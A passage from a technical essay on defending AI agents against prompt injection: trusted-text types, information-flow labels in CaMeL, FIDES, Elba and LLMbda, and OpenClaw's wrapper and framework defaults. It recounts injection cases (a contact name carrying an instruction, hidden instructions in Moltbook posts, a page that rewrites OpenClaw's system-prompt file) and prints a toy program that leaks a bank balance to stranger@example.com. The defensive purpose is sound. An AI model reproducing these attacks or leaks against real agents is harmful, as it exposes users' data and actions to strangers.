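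The labelling rule requires only one trusted type, because it treats both the developer and the authorised user as trusted. To keep users' words out of the system prompt, as GitHub's query does, a team can split `TrustedText` in two.

The builder helps only if developers use it. A team can add an automatic check that rejects any file that imports the provider's library, except the model connection's code, much as Google's compiler rejects the original browser functions.

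### The contact-card bug

OpenClaw wrote a shared contact into the user's message as `<contact: NAME, NUMBER>`, and in Imperva's attack the name contained its own closing bracket and an instruction. With the new builder, similar code would be:

```ts
const text =
  `${message.body} <contact: ${contact.name}, ${contact.phone}>`;
prompt.user(text);
```

Joining the pieces produces a plain string, even though `message.body` is a `TrustedText`. The compiler stops at the last line:

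```
error TS2345: Argument of type 'string' is not assignable to
parameter of type 'TrustedText'.
```

Removing the angle brackets from the name would not clear the error, because the result would still be a string. The straightforward repair is to send the contact separately:

```ts
prompt.user(message.body);
prompt.outside(new OutsideText(contact.name, "contact name"));
prompt.outside(new OutsideText(contact.phone, "contact phone"));
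```

The model now receives the attacker's instruction in a message marked as untrusted. `JSON.stringify` adds a backslash before any quotation mark in the name, so the name can't end its own field and start a new one. The model may still obey the instruction, because the type controls only where the text goes and how the program labels it.

A developer could also clear the error by passing the whole string to `trustAfterReview`. That would bring the bug back, but a reviewer would have to approve the line, and anyone could find it by searching for the function's name.

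If OpenClaw's developers had introduced such types when they fixed the Slack topics, the compiler would have rejected any code that put a folder name into the system prompt as a string. It would also have rejected the wake webhook's system events if the function that creates them required `TrustedText`. The webhook's design was apparently intentional, so the developers might have requested an exception, and a reviewer could then have asked who could write the text.

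Types don't remove the initial work of sorting bugs from false alarms. If the earlier `build_prompt` function were written in TypeScript with this builder, all nine of its system lines would fail to compile. The developer would have to handle even the four harmless ones, by using a fixed list of values or making an exception. But after that, a tenth line with the same mistake would fail to compile as soon as someone wrote it.

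Developers of an existing agent can follow Google's approach and start with temporary exceptions for its old code. The list of exceptions then shows them which prompts they still have to check.

### Python's template strings

Most Python developers insert values into text with an f-string, such as `f"The channel topic is {topic}."`. Python joins the pieces immediately, and the resulting string has no record of which words came from `topic`. Python 3.14 added template strings, which begin with `t` instead of `f`. *PEP 750* (Baker, van Rossum and colleagues, 2024) specifies that a template string produces a `Template` object, which keeps the fixed text separate from the inserted values.

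A prompt library could use this separation to do something like a parameterised query:

```python
def split_prompt(template):
    fixed, outside = "", []
    for part in template:
        if isinstance(part, str):
            fixed += part
        else:
            outside.append(str(part.value))
            fixed += f"[outside text {len(outside)}]"
    return fixed, outside
```

Given `t"The channel topic is {topic}."`, the function returns the sentence "The channel topic is [outside text 1]." and a list containing the topic. The program can put the sentence in the system prompt and send the topic in a separate, labelled message. But the model still reads both as one sequence, unlike a database handling a parameterised query.

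Python doesn't allow code to join a `Template` to an ordinary string, because it's unclear whether the string should count as fixed text, so the developer has to choose. `Template(name)` treats the name as fixed text, even if a stranger wrote it, so a team should review such calls as it reviews calls to `trustAfterReview`.

Libraries already use template strings for other languages. Peck (2026), who helped design the feature, has demonstrated one library for HTML and another for SQL. At least two libraries use template strings for prompts, but neither enforces the labelling rule.

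The *t-prompts* library, according to its PyPI page, records which variable supplied each part of a prompt, so a developer can trace a phrase in the finished prompt back to its origin. But the library doesn't record whether the variable held outside text, and it can turn the whole prompt into a plain string, which no longer keeps the parts separate.

The other library, *promptstrings* on PyPI, can attach a source and version to each message. Its PyPI page describes its handling of template strings as "injection-safe", meaning that it never searches an inserted value for further placeholders. This prevents a value containing `{password}` from pulling in another variable, but a value can still contain an instruction to the model. For templates loaded from a file or database, the library provides `parse_trusted_template`, with a warning to use it only on trusted text. However, one of the library's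 examples inserts a topic into a system message with an f-string. If the topic came from a stranger, the example would have the same bug as OpenClaw's Slack connection.

### Casts and untyped code

A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as another type. In TypeScript, `text as unknown as TrustedText` removes the contact-card error without calling the exception function. Python's `cast` does the same for `LiteralString`, and a comment can tell the type checker to ignore an error. Srinivasan and Bleaney say that their type protects against honest mistakes, not against developers who deliberately bypass it. Wang, Bangert and Kern found that code review made deliberate bypasses a negligible problem at Google, partly because the bypassing code looks so odd.

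Not every bypass looks odd. TypeScript has a type called `any`, which turns off checking for a value, and the standard function for reading saved data returns it:

```ts
const note = JSON.parse(savedNote);
prompt.system(note.text);    // compiles
```

Plain JavaScript code can also pass a string to the builder without an error, because TypeScript's types are removed before the program runs and the code above has no runtime check. A team can add a check to `system` and `user` that raises an error unless the value is a `TrustedText` object. This works like Trusted Types in the browser and catches the saved note, the cast and the plain JavaScript call. It would not catch JavaScript code that creates a `TrustedText` itself, because `private` is removed along with the types.

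Some languages make it harder to bypass type checks. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents an agent system built in Haskell, a language with strict types. One of its agents writes programs that search a computer science database and save bibliographies. The function that saves an entry accepts only values of type `Trusted`, which only the function that fetches entries from the database can produce. A program that tries to save an invented entry fails the type check, and the system returns the error to the model so that it can try again. Haskell normally has a few ways to bypass its types, but a restricted version called Safe Haskell excludes them. Rewriting an existing TypeScript or Python agent in Haskell would take a lot of work, so for most teams a check while the program runs is more practical.

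### Storage and plugins

A type lasts only as long as the program holds the value in memory. When an agent saves a web page's title to a database, it saves the characters but not their type, `OutsideText`. If the program later loads the title as a plain string, the builder still rejects it from the system prompt. But the builder also rejects the user's saved preferences, and a developer might get those working again by calling `trustAfterReview` on everything in the database, including the title.

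Kern's photo-sharing site has the same problem, because its database holds both trusted values and text from users. He handles users' formatted profiles by sanitising the text on the server and carrying the `SafeHtml` type from there to the page. An agent has no equivalent sanitiser, so it should save the source next to the text and turn the pair back into an `OutsideText` when it loads them. For preferences, it could offer the user a fixed list of options and save only the user's choice.

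Plugins in other languages cause a similar loss of type information. A Python tool server can send a TypeScript agent a tool description, but not a TypeScript type. The agent should treat everything it receives over such a connection as `OutsideText`, however the other program labels it. A JavaScript plugin that runs inside the agent is harder to control, because it could change the list of messages after the builder has finished.

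### Reviewing the exceptions

At each call to `trustAfterReview`, the compiler's check depends on human judgment. Google forbade the equivalent functions by default and kept a central list of the files allowed to use them. Before adding a file, a reviewer checked that no safe function would do the job and that the code was simple enough to judge with confidence. Wang, Bangert and Kern say the system is easier to run where all code is in one repository, goes through mandatory review and uses the same compiler. An open-source agent with independently written plugins may lack some of these advantages.

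Agents may also need exceptions more often than websites do, since they can't sanitise a stranger's text and then trust it. The survey by Li, Cui and colleagues found that an average of about 15 sources per agent entered the context under the system role. Some of these should move to a labelled channel and others could become fixed text, which might leave few enough exceptions for system prompts to review by hand. User messages would add a few more.

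The number of calls doesn't show how much text they let through. OpenClaw's agent treats every installed skill as a source of trusted instructions, according to Suwansathit and colleagues. A single exception in the skill loader would therefore cover every installed skill, including malicious ones. It would be safer for the loader to require the user's approval of each skill and store a fingerprint of the approved text, so that any later change needs a new approval.

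## Tracking trust through the model's own output

A type such as `TrustedText` records where text came from only until the program sends it to the model. The reply is an ordinary string that doesn't show who influenced which part. After reading a stranger's web page, the model may repeat an instruction from the page in its own words, save it to memory or turn it into a tool call. To keep tracking trust, the program has to give the reply its own label.

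### The lowest trust in the context

Nobody has a reliable way to tell which parts of its context a model used. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, developers can therefore only assume that it used everything. The reply then gets the lowest trust of anything in the context:

```
trust(reply) = min(trust(item 1), ..., trust(item n))
```

The items are all the messages in the conversation and the descriptions of the tools. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, write the same rule in a more general form:

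```
label(reply) = label(item 1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(item n)
```

The join operator, written ⊔, combines labels into the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as each of them. If the only labels are "trusted" and "untrusted", one untrusted item makes the whole reply untrusted.

The general form also works for secrets. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one document, and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, then only Ben and Cara may read a summary of both. If the lists instead record who could have written each document, the join includes all four people, since any of them might have influenced the summary. Tracking labels like these and checking them before an action is called information-flow control.

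The rule is safe, but it can block legitimate work. For example, a user might ask an agent to pay this month's £60 electricity bill and find out when a museum opens on Saturday. The program allows a payment only if the request for it is trusted.

| Step | What enters the context | Label of the new item | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | the user's request | trusted | trusted |
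| 2 | the electricity company's account number, from the user's saved payees | trusted | trusted |
| 3 | the museum's web page | untrusted | **untrusted** |
| 4 | the model's request to pay £60 to that account | untrusted | untrusted, so the program blocks the payment |

The page contains only opening hours, and the payment is what the user asked for. But the program can't rule out that the page changed the amount or the account, so it stops the payment. It will also treat everything else the model writes in this conversation as untrusted, including any notes for later sessions. If the agent had paid the bill before opening the page, the payment would have gone through.

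Eventually every piece of data carries every label, and the labels no longer help with any decision. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this label explosion. Developers can label smaller pieces, such as single messages or the text from each website, but this doesn't help once a model has read the pieces together.

Labels can also fail by letting untrusted text become trusted again. This occurs if one function doesn't pass the label along, as happened with OpenClaw's scheduled jobs.

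### Splitting the work between two models

An agent can avoid much of this over-labelling if the model that chooses its actions never reads untrusted text. In 2023 Simon Willison proposed having a privileged model plan and call tools while a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text. The privileged model can pass on the quarantined model's answers by name without seeing them. This is stricter than OpenClaw's suggestion of a separate reader agent, because there the main agent reads the summary.

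CaMeL, which Debenedetti and others introduced in 2025, adds code to this design. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, studied it closely. The privileged model writes a program from the user's request before the agent has read any outside data. If the user asks the agent to send the minutes to the address in Bob's latest email, the program might be:

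```
email   = latest_email(sender="Bob")
address = quarantined_model("Find the address in this email.", email)
send_file("minutes.pdf", to=address)
```

The control flow, meaning which steps run and in what order, depends only on the user's request, so the email can't add a step that deletes files. But the email can affect the data flow, meaning the values that pass from one step to the next. If Bob forwarded a message from a stranger, the quarantined model might return the stranger's address. CaMeL therefore runs the program in its own interpreter, which labels each value by its origin and checks a policy before each tool call.

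Garby and colleagues estimated how much protection the split provides without labels, using banking tests that pair 16 user tasks with nine attacks. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a step that would never appear in a program written for the user's task, so it should fail even without labels. In the other 47, the program already contains the kind of step the attacker wants, such as a payment.

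A program can also give an attacker control. One user task is to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two trials with CaMeL's policies off, it wrote a program that matched each instruction in the file to a tool, so an attack in the file succeeded.

Labels have gaps of their own if the interpreter doesn't apply them everywhere. This program, adapted from an example by Garby and colleagues, reveals whether a secret bank balance is above 10,000:

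```
1  rich = True
2  flag = True
3  if balance > 10000:
4      flag = False
5  if flag:
6      rich = False
7  if rich:
8      send_email("stranger@example.com", "rich")
```

When a line that depends on a secret runs and changes a variable, CaMeL marks that variable as secret. If the line doesn't run, CaMeL doesn't mark the variable. If the balance is high, line 4 makes `flag` false and secret, so line 6 doesn't run. `rich` stays true and public, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, line 4 doesn't run, line 6 makes `rich` false, and the program doesn't send the email. The stranger learns something about the balance even though no value marked secret reached the email.

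That example is contrived, but Garby and colleagues found a simpler mistake that could affect ordinary programs. When a program inserted an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, as an agent might when building a prompt, CaMeL treated the result as trusted.

### How FIDES hides untrusted data

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the model choose its next step as it goes instead of writing a whole program first. It works like this:

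1. The user's request enters the context as trusted and public.
2. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the label of each field with the label of the context.
3. If a field would make the context less trusted or more secret, FIDES stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. Other fields enter the context normally.
4. The model can use that name in a later tool call. FIDES then fills in the stored value, which keeps its own label.
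5. Before the call runs, FIDES checks the labels of the call and its arguments against a policy.

In the museum example, the page's text would go into a variable and the context would stay trusted, so the agent could still pay the bill. A policy can also set different rules for different arguments of the same call. For a message, it might require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted text in the body.

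Sometimes the model needs information from a variable. It can read the variable with the `inspect` tool, which lowers the context's trust level. It can also query an isolated model with no tools, whose output goes into a new variable.

Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who wants a calendar event created if any of the last three emails contains a meeting request. The main model has the isolated model answer yes or no, and inspects only that answer. If it is yes, the isolated model extracts the details into another variable, and the main model passes that variable to the calendar without reading its contents. In FIDES, a value's label can include its type, so a policy can accept a yes or no from an email but reject free text from it.

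Instructions in an email can still mislead the isolated model, for instance into returning an empty summary. The design only prevents them from determining the main model's next action.

A second policy protects secrets by letting the agent send information only to people listed as readers on that information's label. In the Varonis test, this would have stopped the agent from sending customer records to an outside address, as long as the records' labels listed only company staff. However, FIDES does not track what an agent reveals through its choice of tools. If an agent reads a private note and then books a clinic appointment, anyone who sees this can guess something about the note.

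### What the FIDES test found

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and Slack. With GPT-4o, 152 attack attempts succeeded against an ordinary agent without policies, and none succeeded against FIDES with its policies. AgentDojo's own scoring counted three successes against FIDES, which the researchers discounted after checking them by hand. They discounted some attacks in the study because the policy allowed the action, so the result shows that no attack broke the policy, but some may still have had an effect.

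Averaged over the four settings, policies reduced the ordinary agent's task completion rate from 84% to 42%. FIDES completed 50% of tasks with policies. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent with policies grew from 8 points to 16. GPT-4o often confused variable names or failed to use the isolated model when it should have.

The policy made some of the failures unavoidable. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and do what it says, which is also what an attacker would want. The model caused other failures. In one Slack task, the user had already named the channel, but the agent listed all the channels. The list was untrusted, so it lowered the context's trust level and blocked the rest of the task.

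Trusted labels don't make the model's decisions correct either. One user asked the agent to change a password if it saw a suspicious transaction. FIDES had hidden the transaction descriptions, and the agent never opened them. It judged one transaction suspicious by its size alone and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because the context was still trusted.

The test probably understates how many tasks FIDES would block in real use. Costa and colleagues treated a field as untrusted only if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. Developers of a real agent don't know in advance which fields attackers will use, so they would have to treat more fields as untrusted.

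### Language-Based Agent Control

Zhou and colleagues put the labels into the programming language instead of a special planner. Their Haskell system, Elba, checks the types of each program the model writes and tracks labels with LIO, an existing library for information-flow control. A tool that sends a direct message has this type:

```haskell
sendDM :: User -> Labeled DCLabel Message -> DC ()
```

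The tool takes a user and a message sealed together with its label. `DC` means the action has to go through LIO, which checks the labels at runtime. A program that used an ordinary network function to send the message would fail the type check.

LIO gives each computation a current label, which becomes more restrictive as the computation reads data. An Elba agent can start a subagent inside a function called `toLabeled`. When the subagent reads a web page, only its own label changes. It returns a sealed result, which the main agent can pass to `sendDM` without opening it. This reproduces the two-model split, except that the subagent can keep using tools as long as its label allows.

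Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language guarantees for every program that passes the type check still holds when a program calls a model. The proof requires the system to check all code from the model before running it. Because developers write the scaffolding in the same language, the guarantee covers their code too, but it doesn't ensure that they chose the right policy or labeled each source correctly.

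The researchers also tested the bibliography agent whose types accept only entries fetched from a database. Running on Sonnet 5, it produced 925 citations, none with a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with web search produced 1,002 citations, 19 of which had such an error.

### What the LLMbda theorem guarantees

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents, called LLMbda, and proved a theorem about every program written in it. A program can copy a conversation with a model, clear it or ask the model for more code to run. Every value carries a label, as does the conversation. LLMbda also tracks which branch a program takes and stops the program if it tries to add to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret. CaMeL lacks a similar check, which made the bank balance leak possible.

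The theorem compares two runs of a program that differ only in their untrusted inputs. Models are partly random, so it compares the probabilities of the outcomes. If the program always finishes with either set of inputs, every trusted output is equally likely in both cases, so an attacker who controls the untrusted inputs can't affect the trusted outputs.

If a version sometimes fails to finish, the probabilities can differ, but only by a limited amount:

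```
D ≤ (p1 + p2) / 2
```

Here `p1` and `p2` are the probabilities that the first and second versions fail to finish, including when a label check stops the run. `D` is half the sum, over all outcomes, of the absolute difference between the two versions' probabilities. If one version fails 10% of the time and the other 20%, `D` can be at most 0.15.

The same theorem also covers secrets, because it holds for any label. The researchers checked the proof with Lean, a program for verifying mathematics. They also wrote the LLMbda interpreter in Lean, so the proof applies to the code that runs the agents.

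The theorem doesn't guarantee that the agent finishes, so an attacker can still stop it. It also treats every data source as part of the program, so it doesn't cover a real mail server or bank. Developers must label those sources correctly and put checks in front of sensitive tools. The protection against untrusted text ends wherever a program endorses that text with LLMbda's `endorse` command, but a second theorem shows that endorsing untrusted text still can't reveal secrets.

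To test the language, Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori. Its model writes a program and first runs it on a made-up version of the user's accounts and files, where it can read error messages and correct the program without seeing any outside text. Only the finished program runs on the real data.

### Comparing the results

The table shows the share of AgentDojo tasks each system completed when nobody was attacking it. The percentages are listed in the same order as the models.

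| System | Tested by | Setting | Models | With policies | Without policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Costa and colleagues | all four | GPT-4o | 50% | 61% |
| CaMeL | Garby and colleagues | banking | GPT-5.2, MiMo-v2.5 | 38%, 38% | 67%, 71% |
| Randori | Garby and colleagues | banking | GPT-5.2, Qwen3.7-plus, MiMo-v2.5 | 75%, 75%, 65% | not tested |
| CaMeL | Zhou and colleagues | Slack | Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT 5.4, Sonnet 5 | 24%, 29%, 24%, 19% | 71%, 76%, 81%, 62% |
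| Elba | Zhou and colleagues | Slack | Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT 5.4, Sonnet 5 | 48%, 43%, 48%, 38% | 86%, 76%, 76%, 67% |

Policies roughly halved the number of tasks that Elba completed and reduced CaMeL's completions even more on Slack. Randori seems to avoid this loss, but its comparison with CaMeL is uneven because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and lets its model endorse untrusted data. Without endorsement, Randori's score fell from 75% to 63% with Qwen3.7-plus and from 65% to 54% with MiMo-v2.5. There were also only 16 banking tasks, so the margins of error are around 20 percentage points.

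Almost no attacks succeeded against any of these systems with policies on. Attacks on Randori succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, both with GPT-5.2 on the same task, in which the user asks the agent to make a payment described in a file. The attacker had replaced the file's contents. No attacks succeeded against CaMeL in the runs that finished, but many runs did not finish.

These security scores are weaker evidence than they seem, because AgentDojo's attacks no longer work well on recent models. In the Slack tests, both Elba and CaMeL resisted every attack even with their policies off. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a fully hijacked model. Whenever a subagent received the attacker's text, they replaced its real task with that text.

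Without policies, Elba resisted 425 of 735 attacks with Opus 4.7 and 621 of 735 with GPT 5.4. With policies, it resisted all 735 with each of the four models. This is the best evidence that the labels work, because the result doesn't depend on the model noticing the attack. However, Elba completed only 40% to 48% of the users' tasks in that test with policies, compared with 67% to 76% without them.

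### Inferring influence with NeuroTaint

NeuroTaint, a tool presented in *Ghost in the Agent*, tries to work out what actually influenced the model. It reads the log after an agent has finished and looks for signs that outside text affected a sensitive tool call:

- an exact marker that NeuroTaint attached to the text when it arrived;
- fragments copied from the text;
- wording with a similar meaning, which can reveal a paraphrase;
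- a match with one small part of a long document, where a single malicious paragraph might otherwise go unnoticed.

If it finds none of these, NeuroTaint has a model judge whether the agent would still have made the call if neutral text had replaced the source. This can detect when a web page caused the agent to use a different tool, even if none of the page's words appear in the call. When an agent saves text to memory, NeuroTaint saves the text's label too and restores it when a later session loads the text.

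The researchers tested NeuroTaint on their 400 scenarios with agents running on GPT-4.1 mini. It missed 13 of the 200 cases in which outside text had an influence, and raised false alarms in 16 of the 200 in which it had none. In ten of the 13 misses, the agent reworded the text or loaded it from memory, so the resemblance was too weak to detect. In the other three, the text changed what the agent did without leaving recognisable words. Most of the false alarms came from outputs that covered the same topic as the source or repeated facts the model could have produced without it.

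The researchers compared this with a detector modelled on FIDES, which missed 92 cases and raised 106 false alarms. This is a poor measure of FIDES itself, because the detector looked for known paths from one tool to another, whereas FIDES controls what the agent may do. The detector raised no alarms on four of the 20 agent frameworks, which account for 40 of its misses. A tracker that applied the lowest-trust rule to a complete log should miss none of the 200 cases, but it would probably raise false alarms in most of the harmless ones.

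NeuroTaint's score may not carry over to other agents, since the same researchers built both the tool and the benchmark. The tool found only 55% of the cases marked as influenced when the agents ran on Claude Opus 4.6. The researchers think stronger models often refused before reaching the sensitive call. The benchmark still counts those cases as influenced, so the figure mixes refusals with real misses.

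### Choosing between cautious and inferred labels

As long as every source has the right label and every function passes labels on, the lowest-trust rule can err only by marking output as less trustworthy than it is. An inferred label can also mark output as more trustworthy than it is. NeuroTaint missed 6.5% of the influenced cases in its main test, and an attacker could try different wordings until one escaped detection. NeuroTaint also runs after the agent has acted, so it can't stop a payment.

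Cautious labels are therefore better for deciding whether to allow a consequential action. Inferred labels are more useful for investigating an incident. They could also help someone decide whether to approve a blocked action by showing which page might have influenced it.

Costa and colleagues mention a compromise that several of them helped develop earlier. It estimates which messages influenced a reply, then has the model write the reply again from those messages alone. The new reply needs only the labels of those messages and is usually about as useful as the original.

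### Who may endorse untrusted data

Some tasks can't succeed unless untrusted data affects an action. To pay a bill that arrived by email, an agent has to use an account number that a stranger could have written. Endorsement allows this by raising the trust label of a particular piece of data.

The safest data to endorse is a value with few possibilities. Garby and colleagues describe an agent that sorts an email into one of a fixed set of categories and puts the category in the subject line of its reply. If there are four categories, an attacker controls at most two bits (log₂ 4) and can't insert an instruction. But even one bit is too much if it determines whether the agent pays a bill. Developers therefore have to consider what the value will be used for as well as how many possibilities it has.

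*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* says that an authorised user, an administrator or the application's developer should set the policy, and that outside content must not extend its own permissions. A digital signature doesn't change this, because it proves who wrote a document, not that the document is safe or correct. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system might raise a document's trust label after a prompt injection detector has passed it, but they warn against relying too heavily on such detectors. If an attacker's text got past the detector, it would have the full authority of trusted text.

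Randori lets the model endorse data in the programs it writes. The model writes the program before it has read anything from outside, so an attacker can't ask it for an endorsement. But Garby and colleagues concede that nothing stops a careless model from endorsing too much. Both successful attacks on Randori depended on an endorsement of the file's contents, without which the program would have blocked them.

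A model could instead propose an endorsement and leave the decision to a fixed rule or the user. Prudentia, an extension of FIDES that Zhou and colleagues mention, lets users endorse data or approve single actions while the agent works. For the emailed bill, the agent could show the user the account number and the amount, and ask them to endorse those two values for one payment. The rest of the email would remain untrusted, and so would the same account number in another request.

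## Safe defaults in agent frameworks

Types and trust labels protect only the agents whose developers use them. A safe default also protects other agents, because it applies even when a developer writes code without thinking about security. Many developers build agents on a framework, a library that assembles prompts and runs tools, so one framework's defaults can affect thousands of agents.

### Escaping by default in web templates

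Websites usually build their pages from templates, which contain gaps for the program to fill. Handlebars, a popular template system, escapes whatever goes into a gap unless the developer asks for the raw text:

```
Hello, {{name}}      escaped
Hello, {{{name}}}    inserted unchanged
```

Handlebars replaces the characters `&`, `<`, `>`, `"` and `'` with harmless codes in any value written inside two braces. A developer who has never heard of cross-site scripting can copy this usual form from the manual and get a safe page. The default also makes mistakes easier to find, because a reviewer can search for a third brace, which turns escaping off, instead of having to notice that a call to an escaping function is missing.

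Google's falling bug counts give some idea of what such defaults achieve, but Google combined escaping templates with types that closed the other routes, so the templates weren't solely responsible for the drop. Developers also have good reasons to switch escaping off, such as displaying formatted text, and can then apply the exception to unsafe text, as in the flaw involving Django's `mark_safe`.

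Many developers now use the same templates for prompts, where HTML escaping protects them only by luck. Some model families mark each speaker with angle brackets, while others use square brackets or a name followed by a colon. Handlebars escapes angle brackets but not square brackets or colons. It also leaves instructions in ordinary words unchanged, whichever markers the model uses. *Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (2026) points out that a developer who follows the official advice is protected against some fake role markers but not others, with no warning about which.

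### Escaping in Microsoft's prompt templates

Semantic Kernel, Microsoft's library for building AI applications, has a safe default for prompts. Developers can write a prompt as a series of messages tagged with roles, which the library turns into separate messages for the model. At first, text inserted into a prompt could contain its own tags, so an email could close the user's message and open a new system message.

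Microsoft's *Protecting against Prompt Injection Attacks in Chat Prompts* (2024) describes the repair. The library encodes all inserted text, splits the prompt into messages, and then decodes the text in each message. The model still receives the email as written, but the email can no longer add a message or change a role.

The developer still decides which message the text goes into. If a template puts a Slack topic in the system message, the topic stays there after encoding. One of Microsoft's examples puts a function's result, which might come from an email, in a user message. Encoding stops that text from escaping the message, but the model still receives it as the user's words, which breaks the labelling rule.

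Developers could switch off encoding for one variable, for the function results in one template, or for every template at once. The third option restored the old behaviour with a single line.

The default also had a gap, because it encoded only plain strings. If a program passed in a customer record, the library inserted the customer's first and last names without encoding them. According to Microsoft's *Encoding Changes for Template Arguments in Semantic Kernel* (2025), the library now raises an error instead. The developer has to encode each field by hand and then set `AllowDangerouslySetContent` for the record.

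An error is much better than an unreported gap, but the setting applies to the whole record. So if someone later adds a company name and forgets to encode it, the library won't raise an error.

Templates written in Liquid, another template language, needed a separate fix. Semantic Kernel's *Mitigating Prompt Injection in Liquid Templates* includes an early plan, since crossed out, to also replace every colon in inserted text. HTML encoding alone would have left the colons unchanged.

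### One function for all context

No escaping function can make a sentence harmless to a model, so an agent framework's defaults have to control where text goes and how the program labels it. The simplest design sends all outside text through one function:

```python
def add_context(text, source, dangerously_trust=False):
    if dangerously_trust and source.kind == "tool":
        raise ValueError("Tool results can't be trusted text")
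    if dangerously_trust:
        context.add(role="system", text=text)
    else:
        context.add(role="tool", text=label(text, source))
```

A developer who writes `add_context(title, page)` gets a labelled message by default. If they forget the last argument, the web page's title can't end up in the system prompt. A tool result can't end up there even if they include that argument. A reviewer can find every exception by searching for `dangerously_trust`. The developer's own instructions can go through a separate function that accepts only fixed text.

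OpenClaw's scheduled-job flaw arose because events were trusted by default, so forgetting a setting left an event trusted. If events had been untrusted by default, the same mistake would only have added an unnecessary label to one of the program's own notices.

A shared function protects the agent only if no other code can call the model directly. McCauley, Schulz and colleagues (February 2026), in *Exploring the Security Risks of AI Assistants like OpenClaw*, found that OpenClaw called models from several parts of its code, with no final point that every request passed through. They recommend creating one, partly so that operators can add their own checks there.

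They also recommend preventing an agent from changing the files that supply its standing instructions. Users would have to approve any change to skills, tools or the system prompt. In their demonstration, a malicious web page got OpenClaw to run a script, which added instructions to a file that OpenClaw loads into the system prompt of every new session. Labelling web pages would not have protected that file. The researchers compare their proposal to a long-standing rule in computer security that a program should not be able to modify the instructions it is running.

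### What OpenClaw's markers cover

OpenClaw's main protection for outside text is a function that puts it between two boundary markers. In the version that Mint Security audited in February 2026, the wrapper began with a notice of nearly 90 words. The notice told the model not to treat the text as instructions, and to ignore any request in it to delete files, run commands or reveal sensitive information. The function then added the text's source, such as an email's sender and subject, followed by the text itself.

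Mint Security's *When AI Agents Browse Unprotected* lists which parts of version 2026.2.9 used this function:

| Source of the text | Wrapped? |
|---|---|
| Web pages opened with the built-in tool | yes |
| Search results from Perplexity and Brave | yes |
| Search results from Grok | no, until version 2026.2.12 |
| Chat channel topics and descriptions | yes |
| Gmail messages and webhooks | yes |
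| Output of shell commands | no |
| Skill files | no |
| Opening message of a scheduled job | no |

The Grok gap shows how easily developers can miss a source of text. The code for all three search services was in one file, but the developers had wrapped the results from only two. Each new source needed its own call to the wrapper, and nothing failed when someone left that call out.

The gap in shell commands mattered more because it let a skill bypass the wrapper. Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, published a skill with instructions for OpenClaw to read posts using `curl`, a command that downloads content from web addresses. OpenClaw would have wrapped the posts if the agent had opened them with its built-in web tool, but with `curl` they arrived as ordinary command output.

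Mint Security cites an estimate that about 2.6% of Moltbook posts contained hidden instructions. The skill had the agent check the site every 30 minutes, and in Mint Security's example the agent loads 15 posts at a time. If the malicious posts are spread at random, each batch has about a one in three chance of containing at least one (1 − 0.974¹⁵).

Scheduled jobs had a different problem. OpenClaw used a session's name to determine whether to wrap its opening message. Gmail and webhook session names began with `hook:`, but scheduled job names began with `cron:`, so OpenClaw treated the jobs' opening messages as its own and didn't wrap them.

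Mint Security read the code but did not test whether a model would obey an unwrapped post. The audit therefore shows which paths lacked a label but gives little evidence of how often that would have mattered.

OpenClaw's developers have since extended the wrapper to more paths. *fix(security): harden untrusted web tool transcripts* applied it to what the agent sees in a browser, including page contents, open tabs and console messages. It also removed some details of tool results from the saved history that the model reads later. OpenClaw also wraps text from uploaded files and text extracted from attached documents. Uploaded files get the markers and a note of their source, but not the long warning that some other wrapped text gets.

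According to the documentation, the step that removes fake role markers covers web pages, files that the agent reads and incoming chat messages. It does not mention shell output. A framework could close that gap by adding a warning label to every tool result when it enters the context. Tool developers would then not have to remember to label results themselves, but the model would also see the warning on harmless results, such as the output of the user's own scripts.

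### One interface for 15 chat apps

OpenClaw connects to each chat service through an adapter, code that translates the service's messages into a common form. Suwansathit and colleagues counted 35 advisories about these adapters in their February set. These were the 13 about approved-sender lists, ten about webhooks that accepted requests without properly checking who sent them, and 12 about leaked credentials or outside text that reached the agent.

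Suwansathit and colleagues propose a shared interface that every new adapter would have to implement. In the sketch below, the first two function names come from their proposal, and the last function is an addition for the labelling rule.

```ts
interface ChannelAdapter {
  // The platform's permanent ID, never a display name.
  resolveAllowlistIdentity(message: PlatformMessage): PermanentId;

  // Must pass the same tests on every platform.
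  verifyPlatformWebhook(request: Request, config: Config): boolean;

  // The only hosts that may receive this platform's credentials.
  credentialHosts: string[];

  // Topics, contact names, location labels and similar text.
  outsideText(message: PlatformMessage): OutsideText[];
}
```

An adapter without one of these parts would not compile. The compiler can't check whether `verifyPlatformWebhook` works correctly, so the researchers want every adapter to pass a common set of tests. They say such tests would have caught three mistakes before release: a missing check for Telnyx, a wrongly skipped check for Telegram, and an exception for Twilio. OpenClaw had documented the Twilio exception as an option and described it only as "less secure".

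A shared interface would not have identified all outside text by itself, because whoever wrote the WhatsApp adapter would still have had to realise that a stranger can choose a contact's name. Imperva notes that MCP gives tools a standard way to connect to agents, but that no standard covers how contacts, locations and similar objects should reach a model. Each product's developers have to work this out themselves.

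OpenClaw has moved towards the proposed design. Its *Channel inbound API* describes a shared function that builds the context for incoming messages. OpenClaw's bundled adapters must pass this function a record showing how the program admitted the sender. The function accepts each record once, and only for the message, session and plugin it was created for. Other plugins can call a public version, but that version can't confirm who sent a message. OpenClaw also offers adapters an experimental shared function that determines which senders and commands are allowed.

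### The Telegram migration tool

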